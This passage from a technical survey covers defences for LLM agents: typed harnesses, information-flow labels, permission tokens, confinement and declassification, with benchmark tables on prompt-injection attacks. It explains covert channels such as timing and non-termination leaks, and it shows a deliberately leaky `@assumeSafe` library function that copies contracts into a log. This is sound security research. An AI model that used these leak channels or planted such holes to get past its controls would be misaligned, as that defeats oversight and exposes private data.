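   agent defs ("Refine the search or finish. First result: " ++ show record)
```

The last line of a `BibIO ()` program must have the type `BibIO ()`, so the compiler requires the sub-agent's code to have that type too. The sub-agent therefore cannot do anything that its parent could not do. The parent can also rule out all side effects by requesting a plain `Int`. It cannot request an `IO ()`, because its own program cannot include `IO` actions such as `writeFile`.

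Zhou and colleagues also proved that if a language's type system guarantees something about the tool calls of every program of a certain type, the same guarantee holds for programs of that type that contain agent calls. This requires the compiler to check each generated program before it runs. The proof replaces every agent call with an ordinary function that queries the model, checks the answer and runs it. Since answers can contain further agent calls, the proof assumes a limit on how deeply the calls nest.

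The theorem holds whether or not the model is honest, because it treats the model as a function that could return any program. It also applies to properties that compare several runs, such as noninterference, if the original language guarantees them. But it only carries existing guarantees over to agents, so a mistake in the developer's library would carry over too.

### Labels that rise as the program reads

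Unlike TACIT, ELBA can keep two customers' contracts apart. It does this with LIO, an existing Haskell library for information flow. Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2012), in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*, describe how it works. Each computation has a current label, and the library applies two rules, where `⊑` means "may flow to":

```
to read data labelled d:              current = join(current, d)
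to write to a place labelled p:       allowed only if current ⊑ p
```

A program for customers A and B might proceed as follows:

1. It starts with a public label and can write anywhere.
2. It reads A's contract, and its current label rises to "A only".
3. It saves a summary in A's folder, which has the same label.
4. It tries to send a message to B, and LIO stops it with an error.

*On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems* (2015) explains that the current label covers everything the computation can access, so LIO does not have to label every variable. Flume similarly puts labels on processes, but a single process can contain many LIO computations. According to *Cryptographically Secure Information Flow Control on Key-Value Stores* (2017), a computation can raise its label but never lower it.

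The fourth step fails at run time, not at compile time. In ELBA, a program that uses LIO has a type such as `DC ()`, whether it sends A's summary to A or to B. The type guarantees only that the program cannot act except through LIO's operations, and LIO compares the labels each time the program calls an operation. Stefan and colleagues chose to check labels at run time because labels can depend on information the compiler does not have, such as the name of a user who joins later.

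The disadvantage is that a program can fail halfway through. In the example, the summary is already in A's folder when LIO blocks the message to B. When the compiler rejects a program, in contrast, everything stays as it was.

LIO's guarantee does not cover information leaked by whether a program finishes, but the library can reduce the risk with a clearance, an upper limit on how far a computation's label may rise. In an example from Stefan and colleagues, a conference system sets each reviewer's clearance so that a program running for a reviewer with a conflict of interest cannot read the confidential review, and therefore cannot leak it.

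A program can keep labels from spreading by reading a secret inside a function called `toLabeled`. The label rises only for the code inside, and the result comes back wrapped in a `Labeled` value. The outer program keeps its low label until it unwraps that value.

`Labeled` looks like TACIT's `Classified` container but has no `map` method. LIO's labels also track trustworthiness, which `map` would undermine. A program could use `map` to apply a function that ignores a trusted value and returns unrelated text, and the result would still have the trusted label.

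With `toLabeled`, ELBA can reproduce the dual-LLM pattern. A sub-agent reads an untrusted web page inside `toLabeled` and writes a message, which the outer agent can send without reading. Unlike the quarantined model in the original pattern, the sub-agent can use tools, because LIO checks each call against the current label.

### What happens when every injection works

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. The table shows how many of the 21 tasks each system completed when there was no attack.

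| Model | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies on | ELBA, policies off | CaMeL, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT-5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

With policies on, ELBA completed almost twice as many tasks as CaMeL. Twenty-one tasks is a small sample, but the results were similar when the researchers paired each task with five attacks. ELBA then completed 40 to 52 of the 105 combinations, depending on the model and the style of attack, and CaMeL completed 22 to 30. ELBA probably did better because its agents can read results and write new code in response, whereas CaMeL's planner has to write its whole program in advance. The two systems also enforced different policies, which may account for part of the gap. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL because each new piece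 of code requires another model call.

Type errors caused few problems. ELBA's agents needed an average of 0.13 retries per run, and only 7 of 2,688 runs ended because the model repeatedly failed to write code that passed the type check.

Every model resisted all 105 attacks in both systems, even with the policies off. AgentDojo's standard attacks can no longer show whether a security policy works for models like these, because an agent without a policy also resists them all. This does not mean the models are safe, as Zhou and colleagues note that OpenAI's automated attack system, GPT-Red, consistently got past the defences of GPT-5.5, a newer model than the one they tested.

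The researchers therefore simulated attacks that always succeed in taking over a sub-agent. ELBA normally gives a sub-agent a task and the data to read. In this test, whenever the data contained an attack, ELBA gave the sub-agent only the attacker's text as its prompt. The researchers ran the 105 combinations seven times with each model, for 735 trials per model.

| Model | Attacks resisted, policies on | Attacks resisted, policies off | Tasks completed, policies on | Tasks completed, policies off |
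|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT-5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

This is much better evidence for the policies than the standard attacks provide. Up to 42 percent of the attacks succeeded without the policies, and none succeeded with them. The first column includes 29 trials that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks because the agent had opened a particular web address. The researchers reviewed all 29 and found that opening the address revealed nothing and broke no policy.

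The policies also reduced the number of completed tasks by 33 to 44 percent. Under them, an agent that reads untrusted data keeps only the privileges of the data's source. This stops an attacker's instructions but also legitimate work that depends on outside text.

The test covers only attacks in which the attacker controls sub-agents that read data, while the top-level agent still works from the user's real request.

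### Filling a gap in a running program

LACUNA, the extension of TACIT in which models write parts of a program while it runs, takes a similar approach in Scala. Each `agent` call leaves a gap for the model to fill. LACUNA inserts the model's code into the surrounding source code, runs the Scala compiler on the result, and executes the new code if it compiles. The model's code can therefore use any variable or function available at that point, and the compiler applies the same rules to it as to code a developer wrote there.

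Zhao and colleagues illustrate the benefit of checking the whole insertion first. An agent has to subtract 50 from an account balance and return the new balance as a whole number. The model writes:

```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The second line produces text, not a number. If similar Python code failed on the second line, the balance would already have changed, and a retry would subtract another 50. LACUNA's compiler rejects both lines together, so the balance stays at 100 and the model can safely try again.

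This protection applies to one insertion at a time. If the model's code changes the balance and then makes another `agent` call, the balance has already changed by the time the model writes the second piece of code. The same is true of ELBA's sub-agents. Code that passes the check can also fail partway for other reasons, such as a lost network connection, or be correctly typed but do the wrong thing, such as subtracting 60.

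The researchers ran about 400 small tests in which they inserted valid or faulty code into a program, and the compiler accepted the valid code and rejected the faulty code every time. They then tried LACUNA on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 difficult questions that an agent answers by searching a fixed collection of documents. With DeepSeek-V4-Flash, it answered 27.1 percent correctly. The compiler rejected 8.6 percent of the generated code, and the agent needed 0.7 retries per question. The researchers did not run an ordinary agent on the same questions, so the result shows that models can work this way but not whether the type checks reduce accuracy. They did run an ordinary agent on the customer-service tasks described earlier, and LACUNA solved fewer tasks than it did.

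On AgentDojo, LACUNA completed more tasks than TACIT in seven of eight comparisons, by 2 to 7 percentage points, but it also let through more attacks. The developer decides which capabilities are available at each gap, and the compiler cannot check whether the task needs all of them.

### Permission tokens in L3M

ELBA and LACUNA rely on the type checkers of existing languages but do not prove their own code correct. *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) presents a harness from Amazon written in Lean, so the developers can program the harness and prove things about it in the same language.

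A person first writes a grant that lists what an agent may do, such as edit one folder or contact certain websites. When the agent starts, L3M creates a token, called a capability, for each permission in the grant. Each token records its limits. Fetching a web page, for instance, requires a token called `NetCap`, which contains the list of permitted hosts. Code without that token cannot express the request, and L3M shows the model only the tools that the agent's tokens cover. A prompt injection can change the model's requests, but it cannot create a token.

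Agents can also write their own tools. If an agent keeps searching a project for TODO comments, it can write a Lean program to do this, which becomes a new tool the next time the agent starts. L3M makes three checks before it accepts the program:

- The source must not contain features that run code during compilation, or use unsafe functions.
- The program must declare which kinds of access it needs, such as reading files, and its type must show that it uses no others.
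- The agent's existing tokens must cover everything the program declares.

The new tool saves the model from repeating the steps one by one, but it runs with the tokens the agent already had, so it adds no permissions. Similarly, an agent can request a sub-agent with a narrower grant than its own, but L3M rejects requests for a wider one.

### Separating private data from the network

L3M's design includes a rule that a process that can read private data may not send data out. L3M enforces this rule automatically only for tasks it runs in containers. Once a step in such a task has had access to private source code, neither that step nor any later one can use the network.

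Elsewhere, the rule depends on the person who writes the grants, because L3M lets that person give one agent both the company's files and access to the whole internet. To follow the rule, the company could split the work between a private agent that reads the contracts but has no network access and a researcher that can search the web but cannot open the contracts. The two would communicate only by messages.

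Eisenach and colleagues calculate how much such a split could leak. Let `S` be the private data, `M` the messages that the private agent sends, `E` everything that the researcher sends out, and `Z` the public information. If the messages have a fixed total length of `k` bytes, then

```
I(S; E | Z)  ≤  I(S; M | Z)  ≤  8k bits
```

Here `I(S; E | Z)` measures how much an outsider who already knows `Z` can learn about `S` from `E`. The first inequality holds because the researcher's only information about the private data comes from the messages, and the second because a byte holds 8 bits. A 100-byte question can therefore leak at most 800 bits, however many web searches follow, which is too little for a whole contract but enough for three 256-bit keys.

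The limit assumes that the agents have no other way to communicate, such as the timing of their messages or a shared file. L3M does not enforce this assumption or count the bytes. The researchers have designed but not built a meter that would record how much of each kind of private data enters an agent. They point out that a cap on this amount would be a safety property in Schneider's sense, so a monitor could enforce it.

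### What L3M proves and what it assumes

Each of L3M's main theorems covers one check in the code that actually runs, and depends on parts of the system that it does not cover.

| Subject | Proved in Lean | Assumed or checked in other ways |
|---|---|---|
| Files | The text of a file path cannot lead out of the agent's folders | A run-time check handles links that point elsewhere |
| Tokens | At startup, L3M creates tokens only for permissions in the grant | Checks during the build stop other code from forging a token |
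| Agent-written tools | An accepted program directly names only permitted functions | Lean's compiler and the code that performs file and network operations are correct |
| Sub-agents | A sub-agent's grant at creation is no wider than its parent's | No person widens it later |
| Undo | L3M can restore a file to its state before a recorded edit | Git, which stores the old version, returns it unchanged |
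| Private data in containers | A plan never restores the network after a step that used private data | The container software follows the plan |

Eisenach and colleagues argue that L3M's separate checks together confine an agent, and they test this, but they acknowledge that they have no theorem for a whole session. In particular, they have not proved that a malicious Lean program cannot affect the computer while L3M is loading it. LLMbda's proof of noninterference covers a complete but very small language, while L3M has narrower proofs about a full harness.

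The theorems about permissions also do not guarantee secrecy, because an agent with permission to read a key and upload files can still upload the key.

### How much work is left

In L3M, an action is called tame if the system can undo it or has limited it in advance with a token. Other actions need review. Editing a project file is tame because L3M keeps the old version, and fetching a page from an approved website is tame because the token limits the destination. Shell commands are not tame because they can do almost anything inside their sandbox and L3M has no general way to reverse them.

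The researchers measured how much an agent can do with tame tools alone, using 37 tasks from Terminal-Bench 4.0.0, a test of command-line work. All the agents used Claude Opus 5 and had three attempts at each task.

| Agent | Tasks solved in at least one of three attempts |
|---|---|
| Claude Code, permission checks off | 59.5% |
| L3M with a shell, review off | 41.7% |
| L3M with tame tools only | 27.0% |
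| L3M with tame tools only, and no agent-written tools | 24.3% |

When restricted to tame tools, L3M solved about a third fewer tasks than it did with a shell, and the number of successful attempts fell by nearly half, from 34 to 18. Letting the agent write new tools changed the number of tasks solved by only one, although the prompts did not encourage it to write them.

Even with a shell, L3M solved far fewer tasks than Claude Code, and its successful attempts used 74 percent more tokens. Eisenach and colleagues attribute this to a harness they have not yet tuned. The limits on authority probably did not cause the extra token use, since L3M used about as many tokens with a shell as without one. The tests included no attacks, so they measure only how much the restrictions hinder the agent.

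In a separate comparison, a second model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, reviewed every shell command before L3M ran it. If the two models still disagree after a short exchange, L3M normally refers the command to a person. This would have happened for 2.4 percent of the commands. Review did not clearly change the number of tasks solved, but it required about 85 percent more model calls and 50 percent more tokens.

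## What do the finer controls still let through?

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes a customer who runs someone else's program on confidential data. The customer needs the results but does not want the program to pass the data to the program's owner. Lampson called this the confinement problem. The contract company is in the customer's position, and the cloud model's provider is in the program owner's.

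A confined program can leak through three kinds of channel:

| Channel | Lampson's example | In the contract example |
|---|---|---|
| Storage | A temporary file that the owner can read | A copy of a contract in an ordinary project file |
| Legitimate | The bill for the service, which the owner has to see | The choice between two approved messages |
| Covert | The load that the program puts on the computer | The time that passes before the next prompt reaches the provider |

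Labels and types mainly control storage and the contents of messages, but some kinds of storage are hard to recognise. Lampson gives the example of a file lock, which stops one program from writing to a file while another has it open. A program that tries to open a locked file learns one bit, even though nobody has written anything. The operating system can close this channel by letting the confined program continue with a private copy, so the other program never finds the file locked.

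### Running time and programs that never finish

TACIT seals the result of a function that processes a contract, but it does not hide how long the function runs. If the function takes longer when the contract mentions penalties, the next prompt reaches the provider later. Odersky and colleagues say they do not cover such leaks. Sabelfeld and Myers list several other covert channels, including whether a program finishes, whether it uses up a shared resource such as disk space, and how much power the computer uses.

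Proofs of noninterference usually leave these channels out. A common version of the theorem compares only runs that finish. By that standard, a program is secure even if it runs forever when the last bit of a key is 1 and prints `finished` when the bit is 0, because every run that finishes prints the same thing. A stricter checker would have to either forbid loops controlled by a secret or prove that each one ends, which no method can do for all programs. Forbidding them would rule out ordinary code, such as a search that stops at the first penalty clause.

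Running time is even harder to include, because it depends on the processor, its memory caches and whatever else the machine is doing. Sabelfeld and Myers conclude that a system protects secrets only relative to a model of what outsiders can observe. A program may be secure on an abstract computer and still leak on a smart card, because the card draws its power from a reader that an attacker may control. The theorem for secure multi-execution covers the number of steps a program takes, but not how long they take on a real machine.

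Researchers often defended the common theorem by saying that a program can leak at most one bit per run through whether it finishes. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues showed in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* that this holds only if the program produces no output while running. Their counterexample counts upwards, prints each number and gets stuck when it reaches the secret. The last number printed reveals the secret, yet well-known information-flow checkers accept the program.

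They also proved that a program which passes such a check can do no better than this kind of exhaustive search, which takes exponentially longer as the secret gets longer. At a billion numbers per second, a 32-bit secret would take at most about 4 seconds and a 128-bit key about 10²² years. The guarantee is therefore strong for long random keys but much weaker for a contract price, which has comparatively few plausible values.

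### Limiting how much can leak

A defender can estimate the damage by counting how many different outcomes of a run an outsider can tell apart:

```
bits per run  ≤  log2(number of distinguishable outcomes)
runs needed   ≥  bits in the secret / bits per run
```

If the outsider learns only whether the program finished, each run has two possible outcomes and leaks at most one bit. Leaking a 128-bit key then takes 128 runs, which an agent could make in a single session.

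Running time can reveal more. If a program may run for up to ten minutes and the outsider can measure the time to the nearest second, there are about 600 outcomes, or 9.2 bits per run. The same key could then leak in 14 runs.

Lampson's defence lets the customer decide what the outsider observes, and the operating system enforces that decision by slowing the program down if necessary. For example, the harness could wait exactly one minute before answering, stop any program still running, and send the same message either way. The timing and content of the answer would then reveal nothing about the contracts. However, a one-second task would also take a minute, and the model could not learn that its program had failed.

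For customers who can accept a small leak, Lampson suggests limiting the capacity of the channel, which is less demanding than closing it. The harness could round each running time up to 1, 10 or 100 seconds and treat failures as 100-second runs. With three outcomes, each run leaks at most 1.6 bits, so leaking the whole 128-bit key would take at least 81 runs. If the company replaces the key after ten runs, an outsider can learn at most 16 bits of it, and the remaining 112 are still far too many to guess.

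The limit on runs has to count retries, parallel runs and sub-agents, or an agent could get around it by starting more programs. The harness should also keep programs from reading the clock, because a program that can time its own steps could report many measurements from one run.

These limits protect keys better than they protect contracts. Sixteen bits of a random key are useless on their own, but sixteen bits are enough to answer sixteen yes-or-no questions about a contract.

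### Releasing part of a contract on purpose

TACIT can show the summary to the user, but other people may need some of the information too. Suppose the company's outside accountant needs the new payment date and amount. Strict noninterference would forbid sending the accountant these details, so the company needs declassification, a deliberate and authorised release.

Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, classify release policies by four questions. The company might answer them like this:

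| Question | The company's rule |
|---|---|
| What may leave? | The payment date and amount |
| Who controls the release? | The finance director, who also names the recipient |
| Where in the program may it happen? | Only in a reviewed library function called `releaseTerms` |
| When may it happen? | After both parties have signed |

How much information may leave is a coarser version of the first question. A policy could limit the number of bits or words without specifying which facts they contain.

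We can write the first rule as a weaker form of noninterference. Let `terms(c)` be the payment date and amount in contract `c`, and let `P(l, c)` again be everything the outsider observes when the public inputs are `l`:

```
for all l, c1, c2:
  if terms(c1) = terms(c2) then P(l, c1) = P(l, c2)
```

If two contracts have the same payment terms, the accountant must not be able to tell them apart. This rule would be ordinary noninterference if `terms` returned the same value for every contract, and would protect nothing if it returned the whole contract.

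A policy that addresses only one of the questions can fail badly. Sabelfeld and Sands describe a shop that may reveal up to four digits of a credit card number with each purchase. If an attacker can choose the digits, a few purchases reveal the whole number. The contract company would make the same mistake if it released one 100-word summary per request and let the cloud model write the instructions for each summary. The model could use one request for clause 1, the next for clause 2, and eventually obtain most of the contract. The company should write the instructions itself and limit the total number of summaries.

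The place of the release matters because the rule above does not account for the effort needed to extract information. Suppose the company publishes a hash of the contract so that a partner can confirm that both have the same version. If we replace `terms` with the hash function, the rule allows a program to send the full text, because in practice no two different contracts have the same hash. To rule out such cases, Sabelfeld and Sands propose the principle of non-occlusion, under which a permitted release must not hide another leak. The company can follow it by allowing only the output of the hash function to leave.

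The release function, `releaseTerms`, should take the original contract as its input and extract the payment terms with code that the company has reviewed. If it accepted any sealed number, the agent's program could pack part of the contract's text into a number and submit it as the amount.

*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) applies a similar idea to untrusted data. Trusted code checks a value and approves it for one field of one tool call. For example, a file path from an error log may fill the path field, but it cannot determine which tool is called or whether the action is approved.

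TACIT has no finished system for such releases. As future work, Odersky and colleagues suggest extending its library with declassification checks, limits on repetition and a log of releases. People can also release data by accident. Eisenach and colleagues note that their permission tokens do not cover text a person copies from the agent's replies. Similarly, a TACIT user who pastes a sentence from the sealed summary into the next prompt sends it to the cloud provider.

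### Asking a person only when a label blocks an action

Some releases depend on circumstances the policy doesn't cover, so a person has to decide. To avoid approval fatigue, the system should ask only when it cannot decide by itself. Prudentia, the Microsoft agent in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, extends FIDES and asks for approval only when an action fails a label check. It also shows the model the labels and the rules for each tool, so the model can look for a plan that needs fewer approvals.

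Prudentia can ask the user to endorse data as well as to approve actions. Suppose an email from an untrusted source lists ten tasks. If the agent reads the email without endorsement, its context becomes untrusted and each of the ten actions needs approval. If the user endorses the email first, the agent can do all ten without asking again. But endorsing the email is riskier than approving a single action, because an attacker's instruction in an endorsed email no longer triggers a check.

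The researchers decided not to let Prudentia ask for declassification in the same way. They argue that whether someone should disclose private data depends on the situation, so a person should approve each disclosure separately. For the contract company, a person would approve the message to the accountant instead of declaring the contract public.

The table shows results on AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini. The first column of figures gives the total number of approvals across all the tasks each agent completed.

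| Agent | Approvals | Tasks completed without asking anyone |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, asks before every consequential action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| The same agent, asks only when a label check fails | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES, asks only when a label check fails | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | About 17 | 59.1% |

With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 approvals, compared with 36.8 for FIDES, but completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2 percent versus 75.7 percent). On a set of browser tasks, such as commenting on a post, Prudentia needed no approvals because the agent could complete them without reading the untrusted text.

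These figures count the questions but do not show how well people would answer them. The researchers assumed a person would approve legitimate actions and stop harmful ones. A label check triggers the question, so an attacker cannot prevent Prudentia from asking, but might still influence the information the person uses to decide. The researchers left the design of the approval screen to future work.

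Like FIDES, Prudentia trusts the planner model, so the contract company would still need a way to keep the contracts from the model's provider.

### When checked code starts another program

Lampson's confinement rules require that if a confined program calls another program that the customer does not trust, the second program be confined too. This rule constantly applies to coding agents, because they have to start compilers, test tools and Git.

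TACIT's type checker covers the Scala code that starts a command, but not the command itself. The new process can open files and network connections with system calls, and `Classified` containers don't restrict it. If it has the user's normal permissions, it can read a contract from the disk and print the text, which TACIT then returns to the model as ordinary output. Odersky and colleagues therefore recommend allowing only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox where security is critical.

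Their examples of safe commands are `git diff` and `sbt`, Scala's build tool. But `sbt` is safe only if the agent cannot change the build. An `sbt` build file contains Scala code that runs outside TACIT's safe mode, so an agent that can edit the file and then start `sbt` can run any code it chooses. Eisenach and colleagues make the same point about Lean, where just compiling a file can execute code in it.

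Sandboxing each command restores some control. For the contract company, the sandbox should hide the contracts folder, block network access and allow writes only to a results folder. If a command has to read a contract, the harness should treat everything the command prints or writes as confidential. Kernel labels such as ActPlane's can help track that output.

L3M cuts a container build off from the network once the build has read private source code. One agent can prepare and compile the program while another runs it, so that neither can both change the code and execute it. For ordinary build files, L3M can require a person to approve the exact contents, and the approval lapses as soon as anyone edits the file.

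### What has to work correctly

Each approach has a trusted base, the components that must work correctly for its guarantee to hold.

| Approach | Trusted base |
|---|---|
| Sandbox around a process | The host's kernel or the hypervisor, and the network proxy |
| Kernel labels, as in Flume and ActPlane | The kernel, the label tracker and any programs that may remove labels |
| Labels in the harness, as in FIDES and Prudentia | The software that tracks labels, the tools, and the planner model with its provider |
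| Types, as in TACIT | The Scala compiler, the tool library, the software that runs compiled code and the local model |
| Types and proofs, as in L3M | Lean's proof checker and compiler, six small C files, the Linux kernel, programs such as Git, and the model provider's interface |

All of these systems run on an operating system, so an attacker who controls the kernel can defeat any of them. A type system adds its own components that must be trusted, but it can enforce rules that the kernel cannot.

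The tool library needs particular attention because every new tool adds to it. Suppose the developer of the company's `diff` function saves one of its inputs to help find bugs:

```
@assumeSafe
object ContractTools:
  def diff(a: String, b: String): String =
    debugLog.append(a)
    compare(a, b)
```

If `debugLog` uses Java's standard file functions, `diff` looks pure, and `@assumeSafe` lets the agent's program call `diff` inside a sealed container. The program compiles and produces the right summary, but each run also copies the old contract into the log. If the log is in an ordinary project folder, the agent can print it.

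This one line breaks the guarantee for every contract that passes through `diff`, even though the compiler and the proofs about capture checking are correct. Tests that check only the output of `diff` would miss the problem. The company can reduce the risk by compiling as much of the library as possible in safe mode, where the compiler would reject the call to Java's file functions. It can also review every use of `@assumeSafe`.

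The company has to check the local model's service separately, because no type checker can inspect what the service does with a prompt.

### Permitted actions can still be wrong

Lampson distinguished leaks from the risk that a program may not do what its owner promised. Unlike most leaks, a wrong result leaves the customer with evidence, but that evidence is easy to overlook when an agent did the work. If the summary leaves out a new penalty clause, someone has to compare it with the contracts to notice, and the company used an agent to avoid that work.

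None of the controls checks whether a summary is accurate. Odersky and colleagues say that preventing wrong results is not one of TACIT's goals, and Prudentia's researchers say that label checks can replace human approval as a defence against attacks but not against a model's mistakes. An agent with permission to pay invoices might pay a genuine invoice twice without breaking any rule about secrecy or trust. A company may want a person to approve actions that are hard to reverse, even when every check passes.

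An untrusted model that is restricted to a few answers can still give a wrong one. Eisenach and colleagues describe an agent that needs to know whether a bug report concerns a particular fault. A sub-agent with no permissions reads the report and may answer only yes, no or unclear. Malicious text in the report has at most log₂ 3 (about 1.6) bits of influence over the main agent, but it can still make the sub-agent give the wrong answer.

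Santos-Grueiro's tests also show that a safe run is not always a successful one. In 400 coding runs, Santos-Grueiro observed no action that got past the authority checks, but only 231 runs completed the task safely.

The policy can also be wrong. If an employee saves a new contract in an ordinary folder, TACIT does not seal it, and the type checker correctly allows the agent to print it. If the company approves the wrong address for the accountant, `releaseTerms` sends the payment terms to a stranger. In tests of ActPlane, badly translated rules were the main reason it missed violations.
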